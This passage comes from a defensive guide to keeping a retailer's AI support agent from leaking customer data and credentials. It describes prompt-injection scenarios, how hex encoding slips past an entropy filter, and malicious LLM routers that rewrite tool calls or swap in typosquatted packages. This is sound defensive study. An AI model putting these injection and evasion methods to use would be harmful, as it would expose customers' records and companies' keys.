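| Ticketing | Reading this customer's tickets, replying to the current one | Attachments, forwarding rules |
| Email delivery | One message to the current customer's address on file | Other recipients, copies, attachments |
| Telemetry | Timings, errors, token counts | Prompts and responses |

The most important rule is that the agent can send email only to the customer's address on file. The agent's tools fill in their own credentials, so a prompt injection can't make them use an attacker's key unless the attacker also gets code running in the container. But a prompt injection doesn't need a key to make the agent put another customer's record in an email. Under the email rule, someone who forges a customer's address gains nothing, because the reply goes to the real customer. An attacker may also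 be a genuine customer, so the agent should be able to read only the current customer's data, in both the customer records and the order database.

Several of these rules depend on more than the path. The proxy has to identify which ticket the agent is answering and find the recipient in the request body. In practice, the retailer would write a small service that offers operations such as "reply to this ticket" and fills in the address itself. This adds custom code to maintain, and Anthropic found that the established isolation software it used worked while the allowlist proxy it built itself failed. The service should therefore do very little and accept only a few simple fields.

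The rules will also cause problems. A provider may rename a path, or a software update may start using a new one, and the agent will fail until someone changes the rule. Some services, including many MCP servers, receive every operation at one address, so the proxy must read the request body to tell a search from a deletion. A customer who wants a copy of her receipt sent to her accountant will have to wait for a member of staff.

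Size limits are easy to add but protect mainly against bulk theft. The largest prompt for the question about the cracked lid is about 36,000 bytes, so a limit of 200,000 bytes per request leaves plenty of room for text. The limit would have to be higher if the model also had to process customers' photos. At 200,000 bytes per request, sending Darktrace's 1 GB file would take 5,000 requests. If the retailer answers 500 questions a day with three model calls each, that is more than three days of normal calls. But 100,000 customer records of 200 bytes each would fit into 100 requests.

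### Binding requests to the organisation's own account

Some services give each account its own hostname. The retailer's allowlist has `retailer.crm.example` for customer records and similar names for ticketing and the vector database, so an attacker's account with the same services would normally have a different hostname. The model API, embedding API, email service and telemetry service each use one hostname for all customers. An attacker who can run code in the container could open an account with any of these four and send data there, so the proxy has to check the credential.

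The proxy can compare the credential with the one it expects, as Cowork's does, or discard any credential the container sends and add the right one itself, which also keeps the key out of the container. Either method needs upkeep. The proxy needs each new token when the old one expires, and requests from developers who use a separate test account will fail. If the retailer later adds a fallback model provider, it has to add that provider's account to the proxy too.

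Some requests carry their credentials in the URL instead of a header. Storage services, for example, can issue a *presigned link*, which lets anyone who has it upload one file for a limited time without a key. An attacker could put such a link in an injected instruction, and a proxy that checks only the usual header might miss it. The proxy should refuse requests that lack the expected credential and shouldn't permit general storage domains.

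### Storage policies that refuse outside buckets

When a workload needs cloud storage, the cloud provider can do part of the checking. Amazon's storage service, S3, keeps files in *buckets*, each of which belongs to an AWS account. Allowing the whole S3 domain would also allow attackers' buckets, so AWS recommends sending storage requests through a private *endpoint*, a connection from the company's network to S3 that doesn't cross the internet. It also recommends attaching a policy to the endpoint that blocks S3 operations on buckets outside the company's organisation, using the condition `aws:ResourceOrgID`.

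This rule works regardless of whose credentials a request carries. Even if an injected instruction supplied the attacker's own AWS keys and bucket name, the endpoint would block the upload. AWS evaluates the policy, so the company doesn't need to decrypt anything.

The policy applies only to requests that go through the endpoint. If the container can also reach S3 over the internet, an attacker can avoid the policy that way, so the firewall has to block that route. The policy will also allow uploads to a bucket inside the organisation that is open to outsiders. AWS's IAM Access Analyzer looks for buckets shared this way.

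A strict version of the policy will block some legitimate traffic, because public datasets, partners' buckets and the buckets where AWS stores container image files all belong to other organisations. Without access to those AWS buckets, a machine that pulls images through the endpoint could fail to start new containers. Each of these buckets needs an exception that names it.

The retailer's agent needs no storage access. The policy would be useful for the indexing job if the retailer keeps the original documents in S3, but it doesn't cover the text that the job sends to the embedding API and the vector database.

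### Scanning for secrets

A proxy that can read requests can also search them for data that shouldn't leave, which companies call *data loss prevention*. Some secrets are easy to recognise because they start with a fixed prefix or match a known credential exactly. For others, a scanner may use *entropy*, a measure of how varied the characters in a string are, because random keys tend to have high entropy. Each different character contributes *p* log₂(1/*p*) bits, where *p* is its share of the string, and the sum of these contributions is the entropy in bits per character.

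The entropy filter that Lan and colleagues tested in their study of web-page attacks blocks any value longer than 10 characters that scores above 4.0. Their own sample key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 20 characters. E and the underscore appear three times each, and 14 other characters appear once:

14 × (1/20) × log₂ 20 + 2 × (3/20) × log₂(20/3) ≈ 3.03 + 0.82 = 3.85 bits

The key passes the filter. The sample fragments, such as `SECR` and `ET_A`, also pass because they are shorter than the filter's minimum length. They would pass even without that minimum, because a string of *n* characters can score at most log₂ *n* bits, or 2 bits for four characters.

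The same limit means that the filter can't block any value of 16 characters or fewer. It also can't block *hexadecimal* text, whatever its length. Hexadecimal writes data with only 16 symbols, so its score is at most log₂ 16, or exactly 4.0, and the filter blocks only scores above that. An attacker could get a whole customer record past the filter by having the model convert it to hexadecimal, which would double its length.

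The filter also blocks ordinary text. The harmless search phrase "parcel delays Newcastle upon Tyne 12 December 2026" scores about 4.19, which is higher than the sample key's score, so any threshold that blocks the key also blocks the phrase.

The keyword filter in the same study searches for words such as "secret" and "api_key". If it is case-insensitive, it would catch the key sent whole but miss the fragments, because none of them contains a listed word. Lan and colleagues suggest comparing several requests to detect a secret sent in pieces. That would help if the pieces went to one destination within a short time, but the proxy would have to store recent requests and therefore more private data.

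Most of the retailer's private data doesn't look like a secret. A home address, for example, is ordinary text, and it belongs in an email to the person who lives there. A scanner would need the recipient's identity to determine whether the message is a leak.

Scanning is still useful for catching accidental leaks. The coding assistant that collected every variable on a PC while looking for a configuration file did not disguise the passwords, so a scanner that checked outbound traffic against a list of the company's live credentials could have caught them. The retailer can compare outgoing text with its nine credentials and expect very few false alarms.

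A company can also stop some files from reaching the model. Anthropic's *Block files and email by sensitivity label, now generally available* describes a setting that stops Claude from reading Microsoft 365 files and emails with labels the company chooses, such as "confidential". Anthropic offers this on a best-effort basis, and it depends on staff labelling the files correctly.

### Human approval

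Another option is to ask a person to approve each risky request. Claude Code launched with this approach, letting the agent read files freely but asking the user before it wrote a file, ran a command or used the network. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of the prompts, and that they paid less attention as the number of prompts grew. The approval rate suggests that saying yes became a habit, but it doesn't by itself show that users made mistakes, because most requests were presumably harmless.

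Anthropic then put the agent in a sandbox that lets it write inside its working folder and denies network access by default. Permission prompts fell by 84%, because the agent could no longer do much harm without asking and many approvals became unnecessary. The 84% figure measures the drop in interruptions, not how many attacks the sandbox stopped. Anthropic also lets the automatic check approve some actions in the user's place. The check catches about 83% of overeager actions and blocks only about 0.4% of harmless commands.

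Some products make the opposite mistake and don't ask the user about requests that can carry data out. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrates a theft from Microsoft's office agent, which approved its own emails and Teams messages. Even when a product asks, the user may be unable to judge the request. Lan and colleagues point out that few people could tell whether a request to "verify connectivity" is genuine, and PromptArmor quotes Willison's objection that it is unfair to expect people who don't program to spot suspicious actions.

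Even expert staff couldn't review every request the retailer's system makes. With 500 questions a day and about ten outside requests per question, they would face 5,000 approval prompts a day. Spending ten seconds on each would take nearly 14 hours, and ten seconds isn't long enough to read an email carefully. If staff instead review only emails that break the recipient rule, such as a receipt for an accountant, they might see ten a day. The approval prompt should show the actual recipient and the full text, because an attacker could manipulate a summary written by the model.

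### Tracking where data came from

All of these controls inspect a finished request. *Information-flow control* instead tracks data through the program and uses its origin to decide where it may go. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes two kinds of label. An *integrity* label marks data as trusted or untrusted, and a *confidentiality* label marks it as public or secret, or lists who may read it. When a program combines data from several sources, the result takes the strictest label of each kind, so it is untrusted if any source is untrusted, and only people allowed to read every source may read it.

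Lan and colleagues propose *taint tracking*, a version of this for the attack they studied. The program would mark text from a web page as tainted and block it from influencing the arguments of a network tool. A scanner would classify a four-character fragment of a key as harmless, but the fragment's history would still show that a web page had prompted the request.

This is hard to apply to an ordinary agent because a model reads its whole context at once, so any part of the context could have influenced any word of its output. Once the agent reads one untrusted email, everything it produces from then on has to carry the untrusted label, and a strict rule would block nearly every useful action.

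CaMeL and FIDES, two research designs from 2025, avoid this by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. They build on Willison's *Dual LLM pattern*. In CaMeL, one model reads only the user's request and writes a short program to carry it out. A second model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted data when the program calls it. A custom interpreter runs the program, records where each value came from, and checks a policy before every tool call, as *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) explains.

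For the retailer, such a program might look like this:

```python
ticket = current_ticket()
record = get_record(ticket.customer_number)
order  = get_order(ticket.customer_number)
policy = find_policy("damaged item")
reply  = reader_model("Answer this customer.",
                      ticket.text, record, order, policy)
send_email(to=record.email, body=reply)
```

Suppose the customer's message contains an instruction to fetch another customer's record and send it to a second address. The reader model may follow the instruction, but it can only return text, and the program has already fixed which record to fetch and where the email goes. Before sending the email, the interpreter also checks that the recipient is allowed to read everything that went into the reply. If a bug had included someone else's record, the labels would show that the customer isn't allowed to see it, and the interpreter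 would refuse to send the email. The same check would catch an agent that put a home address into a web search, even without an attack.

Researchers usually test these designs on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office-style tasks while the data they read contains injected instructions. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security*, CaMeL stops nearly all of the benchmark's attacks while completing a comparable share of tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) reports that CaMeL is substantially more secure than three other defenses, though it completes modestly fewer tasks: marking untrusted text, repeating the user's instructions after that text, and filtering the available tools. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), which introduced FIDES, reports that FIDES completes a wide range of tasks securely, with a modest loss compared to unprotected agents.

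These results don't transfer directly to customer support. AgentDojo assumes an honest user whose data may be hostile, and CaMeL relies on that assumption when it builds its program from the user's request. The retailer can't assume its customers are honest, so it would have to treat their messages as untrusted data and take the plan from its own instructions. The planning model would then have to write a program without seeing the customer's request. The reader model could match each message to a fixed list of problems, such as "damaged item" or "late parcel", and the program could have a branch for each. Unusual questions would go to a member of staff.

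Labels can also be wrong or too strict. If the retailer marks its returns policy as trusted, a hostile paragraph added to the policy will be trusted too. If a model reads a customer's record and then writes a search phrase about a broken lid, the phrase inherits the record's label, so the interpreter won't send it to the embedding API even though it's harmless. The program above avoids this by using a fixed phrase, which will sometimes find a less relevant passage.

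FIDES enforces what its paper calls *explicit secrecy*, which covers data that a program copies into an output. A program can also reveal information through its choice of action. If it emails an apology voucher only to customers whose private notes mention an earlier complaint, the voucher's arrival reveals that the notes mention one, even though the email contains none of their text. This leaks little information at a time and is a small risk for the retailer compared with an email that contains a whole record.

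*Can CaMeLs Talk?*, a more recent paper, extends the approach to teams of agents. In its example, a database agent reads an injected instruction and passes it to the coordinating agent. Each agent receives the instruction as tool output, so CaMeL treats it as untrusted in both places. This matters because, as Anthropic warns, attackers gain a new way in when a system trusts its sub-agents' reports more than raw web text. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* also predicts that CaMeL will reduce task completion less as models get better at planning and writing code, which seems likely.

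The retailer can get much of the benefit without a full research system if its developers write the fixed program themselves, let the model draft only the reply, and have ordinary code choose the records and the recipient. They should run the policy checks outside the agent container, because an attacker who runs their own code inside it, as the React2Shell attackers did on web servers, could skip any check that runs there.

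## Keeping credentials out of the workload

A stolen credential gets around most of the controls described so far. The allowlist, the proxy and the size limits apply to requests that leave the retailer's network, but a thief can copy a key to their own computer and use it from there until someone revokes it. The support agent's container now holds eight credentials, one for each of its seven outside services and one for the order database. The browsing container holds two more, for web search and for its own model calls. If neither container held a usable key, an attacker who took one over would have no key to copy.

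### Where credentials end up

| Place | How a credential gets there | Who can read it |
|---|---|---|
| Image layers | The build copies a settings file or source code into the image | Anyone who can download the image |
| Environment variables | The operator passes the key to the container when it starts | Usually every program in the container |
| Mounted files | The operator shares a folder that contains a key file | Any program that can read the folder |
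| Logs | A tool prints its settings, or monitoring records full requests | Staff and the monitoring company |
| The model's context | A tool's output contains a key, or someone pastes one into a message | The model provider, and anyone who can get the model to repeat it |

A container image consists of layers, each holding the files that one build step added or changed. If a later step deletes a file, it no longer appears in the running container but remains in the earlier layer. Many developers keep their keys in a `.env` file and copy the whole project folder, including that file, into the image.

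*Thousands of Exposed Secrets Found on Docker Hub, Putting Organizations at Risk* (Morag, 2025) reports on keys leaked in container images. Morag works for Flare, which sells monitoring for leaked secrets. Flare scanned images uploaded to Docker Hub in November 2025 and found 10,456 that exposed at least one key. About 42% of these exposed five or more. Keys for AI models were the most common kind, at almost 4,000. Flare traced 101 of the accounts with serious leaks to identifiable companies, including a large national bank. Morag doesn't give the total number of images scanned, so we can't calculate what share of them exposed keys.

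Many strings that look like keys don't work. In *Containers Don't Keep Secrets*, a study for the security company Binarly, Pagani and Ivanov (2026) searched more than 90,000 Docker Hub accounts and found 98,816 such strings. More than 50,000 of these came from seven files of application data. They confirmed that 199 keys worked, including 81 for OpenAI, Hugging Face or Anthropic. The real number is higher, because they could check only some types of key and others had expired before the scan. Morag says that Flare's images included live credentials, but doesn't say how many of the keys worked.

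Many credentials also leak through public code. GitGuardian (2026), which sells tools for finding secrets, counted 1,275,105 leaked keys for AI services on public GitHub in 2025, up 81% in a year. It also found 24,008 secrets in configuration files for MCP, the standard for attaching tools to models, and confirmed that 2,117 of them worked. Popular MCP set-up guides often include instructions to paste the key into such a file.

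Morag recommends passing keys to the container as environment variables when it starts, which keeps them out of the image. But Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) point out in *CapSeal* that an agent that can use a key by reading it can also reveal it. An agent with a command line can print all its variables with one command. The coding assistant that lost its configuration file leaked live passwords in much the same way. The retailer's agent has no command line, so the main danger to its variables is an attacker who runs code in the container.

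Mounting a folder as read-only doesn't protect the keys inside it, since an attacker only needs to read them. Anthropic lists files to leave out of any folder that an agent can read, including `.env`, cloud credentials, package-registry tokens and private keys. *Caging the Agents* (2026) reports that an audit of a group of healthcare agents found keys in shell start-up files, in `.env` files, and in configuration files that any user of the machine could read.

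### Keys in the model's context

Ordinary software can leak keys into logs, but an agent can also leak them to its own model. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied *skills*, packages of instructions and code that users add to an agent. From a random sample of 17,022 skills in a large public marketplace, they used automatic filters to pick out 3,156 that handled credentials in suspicious ways. They ran those in Claude Code with fake keys and reviewed the suspicious results by hand. Of the 17,022 skills, 520 (3.1%) leaked credentials, 437 by mistake and 83 on purpose.

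The 437 careless skills had 1,371 problems, and 1,007 (73.5%) were leaks through output such as debugging messages. While testing, a developer adds a line that prints a token and forgets to remove it. On an ordinary server, the token would end up in a log, but an agent's framework adds the printed text to the model's context, so the token goes to the model provider with every later call. An attacker can then inject an instruction to repeat the token. One skill for Google's office applications printed both of the user's login tokens.

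The retailer's agent has no skills installed, but its own tools also return text to the model. If the email tool fails and returns the whole failed request as an error message, the email key in that request enters the model's context. Tools should return a short error code instead.

### How credential injection works

*Credential injection* means adding the real credential to a request at a proxy, so that the workload never holds it. A call from the retailer's agent to the model API would go like this:

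1. The container starts with a placeholder such as `MODEL_API_KEY=placeholder`. It needs some value because many client libraries won't start without a key.
2. The agent's program sends its request to the egress proxy, with the placeholder where the key should be.
3. The proxy compares the destination, method and path with its rules.
4. If a rule matches, the proxy gets the real key from a separate secret store and overwrites the placeholder.
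5. The proxy forwards the request over an encrypted connection and passes the reply back.

simedw describes V7's version, which uses mitmproxy, an open-source proxy that can decrypt and change web requests. The retailer's rules for two of its services could look like this in the same software:

```python
from mitmproxy import http

RULES = {
    ("api.model.example", "POST", "/v1/messages"):
        ("x-api-key", "support-agent-model"),
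    ("api.embed.example", "POST", "/v1/embed"):
        ("x-api-key", "support-agent-embed"),
}

class InjectKey:
    def request(self, flow):
        r = flow.request
        rule = RULES.get((r.host, r.method, r.path))
        if rule is None:
            flow.response = http.Response.make(403)
            return
        header, secret_name = rule
        r.headers[header] = read_secret(secret_name)

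addons = [InjectKey()]
```

The function `read_secret` stands for whatever fetches a key from the store. The proxy must choose the key based on the server it connects to, not the hostname in the request's header. Otherwise, code in the container could connect to one approved service while naming another, and the proxy would send the second service's key to the first.

Overwriting the key also defeats uploads that use an attacker's key, as in the Cowork attack. In Anthropic's phishing exercise, injecting credentials outside the workload would have left Claude with no cloud credentials to send.

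Several products now work this way. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a proxy on the host machine that injects keys only into encrypted requests, while the agent sees the value `proxy-managed`. Anthropic's *How agent identity works* describes a proxy for Claude Tag, the company's agent for Slack. If a request's destination matches a connection an administrator has set up, the proxy attaches that connection's credential. If the destination is allowed but has no connection, the request goes out without a credential. The proxy blocks all other requests. AWS expects a signature made with the key instead of the key itself, so the proxy signs each request to AWS.

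### How a key can still get back to the container

A service can send a key back after the proxy has added it, for example in an error message that repeats the request's headers. For some secrets, Docker searches each reply for the key and common encodings of it, and masks what it finds. Docker warns that this can't guarantee secrecy, because a service could split the key across several fields or change it in some other way.

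OpenAI's *Shell* describes a similar feature for containers that OpenAI hosts, in which the model sees only a name such as `$API_KEY`. OpenAI says the real value never appears in the model's context. But its sample code sends a test key to httpbin.org, which returns a request's headers to the sender, so the key would stay out of the context only if it were also masked in the response. The retailer should inject keys only for services it trusts not to return them.

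Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a credential-injection product made by their own employer, Corvic AI, for leaks. They ran code in its sandbox that made a successful GitHub request without holding a key. They then searched for the key in environment variables, in the request as visible to the code, and in 12 common file locations. They also called an unrelated API and three sites that echo requests back, to check whether the proxy would send the key to the wrong place. All 16 checks passed.

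A second connection, to an economic data service, failed without leaking the key. The service expects the key in the web address, but the product put it in a header. Sixteen checks by the product's maker show that the basic mechanism works in that product. The team didn't test redirects or an approved service that an attacker had taken over. An injected key seems more likely to leak in those cases.

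### A tool that makes the call outside the container

Adding credentials at a proxy suits services that the agent's program calls directly. The other option is a custom tool that runs outside the container, holds the key and makes the whole call. The small service proposed earlier, which fills in the recipient of each reply, can also hold the email key.

| | Injection at a proxy | Custom tool outside the container |
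|---|---|---|
| What the agent sends | The full request, with a placeholder | A few simple fields |
| Adding a new service | A rule and a key | Code for each operation |
| Decryption | The proxy must be able to read the request | Not needed |
| Protocols | Usually web requests only | Any |
| What a manipulated agent can do | Anything the proxy's rules allow | Only the operations the tool offers |

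The order database needs a custom tool, because databases usually have their own protocols and Anthropic notes that Claude Tag's proxy can't carry these. Customer records, ticketing and email should also go through custom tools, because the retailer has to check which customer each request concerns. Credential injection is enough for the model API, embeddings, vector search and telemetry, and the agent can keep its existing client libraries for them. The container then holds none of the eight real credentials.

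A workload that shares the proxy with others still needs a way to identify itself. V7 gives each run of an agent a short-lived token, which the proxy uses to determine who is running the agent and what the run may do. An attacker who stole the token could use it only from somewhere that can reach the proxy, and only until it expires.

A proxy can also make some of the checks that a custom tool would. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes a proxy for Git. Git logs in to it with a limited credential, and the proxy checks, for instance, that the agent is sending code only to the branch configured for the session before attaching the real GitHub token. Jin and colleagues want to replace keys with permissions for narrowly defined actions, which the agent can use but can't pass on. They have built a prototype and set out a plan for testing it.

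### What injection doesn't prevent

Injecting the key at a proxy prevents its theft, but a manipulated agent can still misuse the access it grants. If an email tricks the retailer's agent into requesting another customer's record, a proxy that only injects keys will add a valid one to that request too. The check on which customer the agent is serving must block that request. Anthropic similarly warns that anyone in a Slack channel can ask Claude Tag to use the credentials connected there, so everyone in the channel can effectively read whatever the connected account can read.

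Kenney and colleagues scored several threats before and after credential injection by multiplying likelihood by impact, with a maximum of 25. The score fell from 25 to 4 for a secret pasted into a prompt, from 25 to 12 for prompt injection, and only from 20 to 15 for a key with excessive permissions. These scores are the team's judgements, not measurements. The 12 for prompt injection looks too low for the retailer, whose main worry is losing customer records, because an agent with an injected key can read as many records as before.

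An agent might also use its access to create a new key, and the reply would give it a real credential. Claude Tag's proxy has a setting that refuses such requests to Google Cloud. Anthropic lists dozens of Google services that the setting blocks completely, along with methods on other services whose names suggest they return a token, password or key. Such a long list is hard to keep complete. It is safer to give the agent's account no permission to create credentials and to use the proxy's block as a second layer.

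The secret store, the proxy and the custom tools together now hold every key, just as an LLM gateway holds the keys for model providers. They therefore need stronger protection than the agent container did. They should not run any code that the model writes, and few staff should have access to them.

### Separate keys with narrow permissions

The remaining measures limit how useful a key is to someone who obtains it anyway. The retailer should start by giving each workload its own key for each service. The support agent needs eight keys and the browsing container two. The indexing job, which prepares internal documents for search, needs one for embeddings and one for the vector database. That makes 12 keys, compared with nine if the workloads shared one key per service. With separate keys, the retailer can see which workload a suspicious request came from, and can revoke the support agent's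 embedding key without stopping the indexing job. Anthropic recommends a dedicated account for the agent in each service for the same reasons.

Separate keys can also have separate permissions that match the operations the proxy already allows. The support agent's vector-database key can only search, while the indexing job's key can add passages, so a thief with the agent's key can't add a false returns policy. The order-database account can read only the tables that show items, prices and deliveries, and it can't write to any table.

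These limits have to be set at the service itself wherever it supports them, because a thief who uses the key from another computer bypasses the proxy's rules but not the service's. Morag describes a company that published a GitHub token with full administrative rights, including the power to delete its code. Pagani and Ivanov found a token that could administer 27 organisations' accounts on Terraform, a service for managing cloud systems. A read-only token in either image would have been a much smaller problem.

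Some services can also be set to accept a key only when the request comes from a listed network address. This is easy to set up with an egress proxy because all the retailer's requests come from the proxy. Someone who stole the key would then have to send requests through the proxy, where the other rules apply.

### Spending limits

A thief who steals a model key can run their own prompts at the retailer's expense, even if the key gives no access to private data. At 500 questions a day and 16,000 tokens per question, the support agent sends about 8 million tokens a day. A daily cap of 16 million would leave room for a busy day and limit the loss. The browsing container should have its own, much lower cap, since a hostile web page could make its model waste tokens. If a provider offers no suitable cap, the proxy can count tokens itself, but it can't count those a thief uses in requests that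 bypass it.

A cap, like a size limit on requests, does little to stop the theft of a few records. It also lets an attacker shut the agent down by using up the allowance. An alert at 12 million tokens would give staff time to investigate the cause first.

### Short-lived tokens and workload identity

A conventional API key works until someone replaces it. *Workload identity* avoids storing such a key, by letting a program prove what it is and receive a temporary token:

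1. The cloud platform gives the program a signed statement of its identity.
2. The program sends the statement to the service that issues tokens.
3. The issuer checks the signature and looks up what this program may do.
4. The issuer returns a token that expires after, say, an hour, and the program asks for a new one when it needs it.

The retailer should give this identity to the proxy and the custom tools, not to the agent container, where an attacker who got inside could use it to request tokens. Claude Tag can use such identities for AWS and Google Cloud, but many business applications still issue only long-lived keys. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, finds that agent software has no standard practices for protecting credentials.

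A shorter lifetime gives a thief less time to use a stolen credential. A credential stolen at a random moment has, on average, half its lifetime left. That is 45 days for a key that the retailer replaces every 90 days, and 30 minutes for a one-hour token. Using the token instead of the key therefore cuts the thief's average time by a factor of 2,160.

The 45-day figure holds only if someone replaces the key on schedule. In January 2026, GitGuardian retested secrets that had worked in 2022 and found that more than 64% still worked, so a thief with one of them could have used it for years.

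The factor of 2,160 can also overstate the protection. Half an hour is enough time to copy a customer database if the token can export it. An attacker who stays inside a machine that receives new tokens can take each one as it arrives. Pagani and Ivanov found that automated builds had copied their own temporary tokens into images, some of which went online before the build had finished and the token had expired. Anyone watching for new releases could briefly use the token, and each new build gave them another chance.

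Many services also issue a *refresh token* with each short-lived one. It lasts much longer and is used to obtain new short-lived tokens. A thief who gets both can keep access for far more than 30 minutes, so the refresh token needs the same protection as a permanent key.

### Revocation

A leaked key keeps working until someone revokes it at the service that issued it, even if the key has been deleted from the file that exposed it. Morag reports that about 25% of developers removed an exposed key from Docker Hub within a day or two, but in most cases nobody revoked it. Chen and colleagues found that after developers removed keys from their skills, the same keys remained in more than 50 copies that other people had made.

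Injection makes replacement much easier, because the retailer has to change the key in only one place. For a routine replacement, the retailer creates a second key, puts it in the store, checks that the agent still works, and revokes the first. The proxy may cache the old key, and the agent's requests would fail if the retailer revoked that key before the proxy fetched the new one. Docker's proxy, for example, keeps service keys fetched from an outside store for 55 minutes by default. Practising replacement in advance is worthwhile because staff will have to work faster, and in a different order, after a theft.

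### The Salesloft Drift thefts

A company can also lose data through a credential it gave to someone else. Drift is an AI chat agent for companies' websites, sold by Salesloft. Many companies connected it to Salesforce, where they keep customer records, and Drift held the access tokens for those connections. In August 2025, an attacker stole the tokens.

*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), a report on Google's investigation, describes how an attacker used stolen Drift tokens to log in to customers' Salesforce accounts from 8 to 18 August. The attacker counted the records, exported large amounts of data, and searched it for more credentials, including AWS keys, passwords and tokens for Snowflake, a data-storage service. Salesloft and Salesforce revoked the tokens on 20 August. Google later found that the attacker had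 also used tokens for Drift's email connection to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts, and advised Drift's customers to treat every token connected to Drift as stolen.

Google's report gives no number of victims, but Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 potentially affected organisations, some of which may have lost nothing. The requests appeared to Salesforce to come from an application that each customer had approved, so the attacker didn't need a flaw in Salesforce's platform. Nothing in the published accounts suggests that prompt injection played any part.

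Keeping keys out of their own containers wouldn't have helped Drift's customers, because Salesloft held the tokens. Narrow permissions would have helped if they had limited each customer's token to reading the few fields that a chat agent needs. An attacker with only one-hour access tokens would have lost access long before 20 August, but this attacker had also stolen refresh tokens.

The retailer has the same kind of exposure through any outside company that connects to its customer-record or ticketing system. It should list those connections, revoke the unused ones, and reduce the permissions of the rest. It should also search its old tickets for passwords and keys and revoke any it finds. Staff and customers often paste credentials into support messages when something urgent has broken, and the Drift attacker searched for them.

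## Choosing and checking the services and libraries that handle the traffic

The model provider has to read the retailer's prompts, including any private data in them, to respond. Any service or library that carries a prompt to the provider can read it too. An allowlist can't protect the data from these companies because it has to let them receive it. The retailer therefore has to choose the companies and libraries carefully, send them only what they need, and keep checking them after approving them.

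### Direct calls, gateways and routers

A program can call a hosted model's provider directly, through an LLM gateway that its own organisation runs, or through an LLM router that another company runs. LiteLLM is a popular open-source gateway. Both gateways and routers offer conveniences such as one request format for every provider and a fallback when one is down. Routers also sell access at lower prices, or in places where providers don't offer it directly.

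| | Direct calls | Self-run LLM gateway | Third-party LLM router |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who can read prompts and replies | The provider | The provider and the gateway's operators | The provider, the router, and any further router behind it |
| Who holds the provider keys | Each application, or its egress proxy | The gateway | Usually the router |
| What one break-in on the way exposes | One application's keys and prompts | Every provider key and every application's prompts | Prompts from all the router's customers, and any credentials in them |

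A break-in at the provider itself could expose stored prompts in all three arrangements.

A router can read, copy or change the full text of a prompt, even when the connections use TLS. The customer enters the router's address as the destination, so the encrypted connection ends at the router, which then opens a second one to the provider.

### What 428 routers did

Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) tested how often routers abuse this position in *Your Agent Is Mine*. They bought access to 28 paid routers from storefronts on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify, and collected 400 free ones from public communities. Crosley (2026) describes their method in *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*. The team opened an account with each router, ran a coding agent through it in a sandbox, carried out every tool call the router returned, and watched for unexpected connections and changed files. They also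 sent *canary* credentials through the routers, which were AWS keys that the team owned and monitored, so any use of a key showed that somebody had copied it.

| Behaviour | Paid (28) | Free (400) | Share of all 428 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rewrote a tool call to run an attacker's code | 1 | 8 | 2.1% |
| Used a planted AWS credential | 0 | 17 | 4.0% |
| Emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet | 0 | 1 | 0.2% |

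Two of the free routers hid their attacks well enough that a short trial would have missed them. One began attacking only after the first 50 requests. The other attacked only agents that ran commands without asking the user, and only in projects written in Rust or Go.

These shares don't estimate the risk of an established service, because the sample came from a market in cheap and resold access, mostly in Chinese-language shops and forums. Most of the free routers were built from two open-source templates. The team didn't test the well-known router OpenRouter or routers sold to large companies. The paid sample was also so small that finding one dishonest router in 28 is compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 0.1% to 18%, even if the 28 were a random draw from their own market.

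Within that market, the shares of malicious routers are probably too low. The tests would count a router as harmless if it had copied a credential but not yet used it, or if it attacked only after a trigger that the tests never produced.

An honest router can also pass prompts to a dishonest one. Crosley describes a reseller who buys from a second reseller, who uses OpenRouter to reach the company that runs the model. The customer sees only the first reseller. To study how a route that looks honest can become compromised, Liu and colleagues set up decoy routers with weak security. Other people's routers began sending traffic through the decoys, which received 99 credentials from 440 sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In 401 of those sessions, the agent ran commands without asking for approval, so it would also have run a command that a router had rewritten.

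A router could insert a link to a fake refund page into a reply drafted by the retailer's support agent, and the agent would email it to the customer from the retailer's own address. The agent has no command line, so it couldn't run an attacker's command. The router would also receive about 8 million tokens a day, drawn from all four private sources. No saving on model costs would justify sending that data through an operator the retailer knows nothing about.

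### Three defences on the customer's side

Liu and colleagues tested three defences that a customer can install without help from the router or the provider. According to Crosley, all the results come from artificial examples the team generated.

A *policy gate* checks each tool call before the agent carries it out and refuses commands that download from unlisted domains or install unlisted packages. The gate blocked every ordinary attack and wrongly blocked 1.0% of harmless commands. It blocked no attacks when the attacker knew about the gate and put the malicious code on a permitted domain. The package list matters as much as the domain list, because a router can change `pip install requests` to `pip install reqeusts`, and the misspelled package would come from the same trusted site.

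*Anomaly screening* scores each tool call by how suspicious it looks. It flagged 89.0% of plain attacks but only about half of those that swapped a package name or waited for a trigger. It also flagged 6.7% of harmless calls. When the false-alarm rate was limited to 1%, it caught 43.5% of plain attacks and almost no package swaps. Neither setting looks practical for automatic blocking in an agent that makes thousands of calls a day.

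The third defence is a log of every request and response. Investigators can use it after an incident to find which sessions went through the bad router, but it does not block attacks.

The retailer's custom tools already do much of what a policy gate does, since they accept only a few simple fields and set the email recipient themselves. But they can't detect whether the model or a router wrote the text of a reply. The agent could check this if the provider signed each response, but Liu and colleagues found no major provider that does. Signatures also wouldn't stop a router from reading the prompts.

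### The LiteLLM compromise of March 2026

An organisation that runs its own gateway no longer has to trust a router's operator, but it must trust the gateway's software. On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of the LiteLLM package on PyPI, the main public repository of Python packages.

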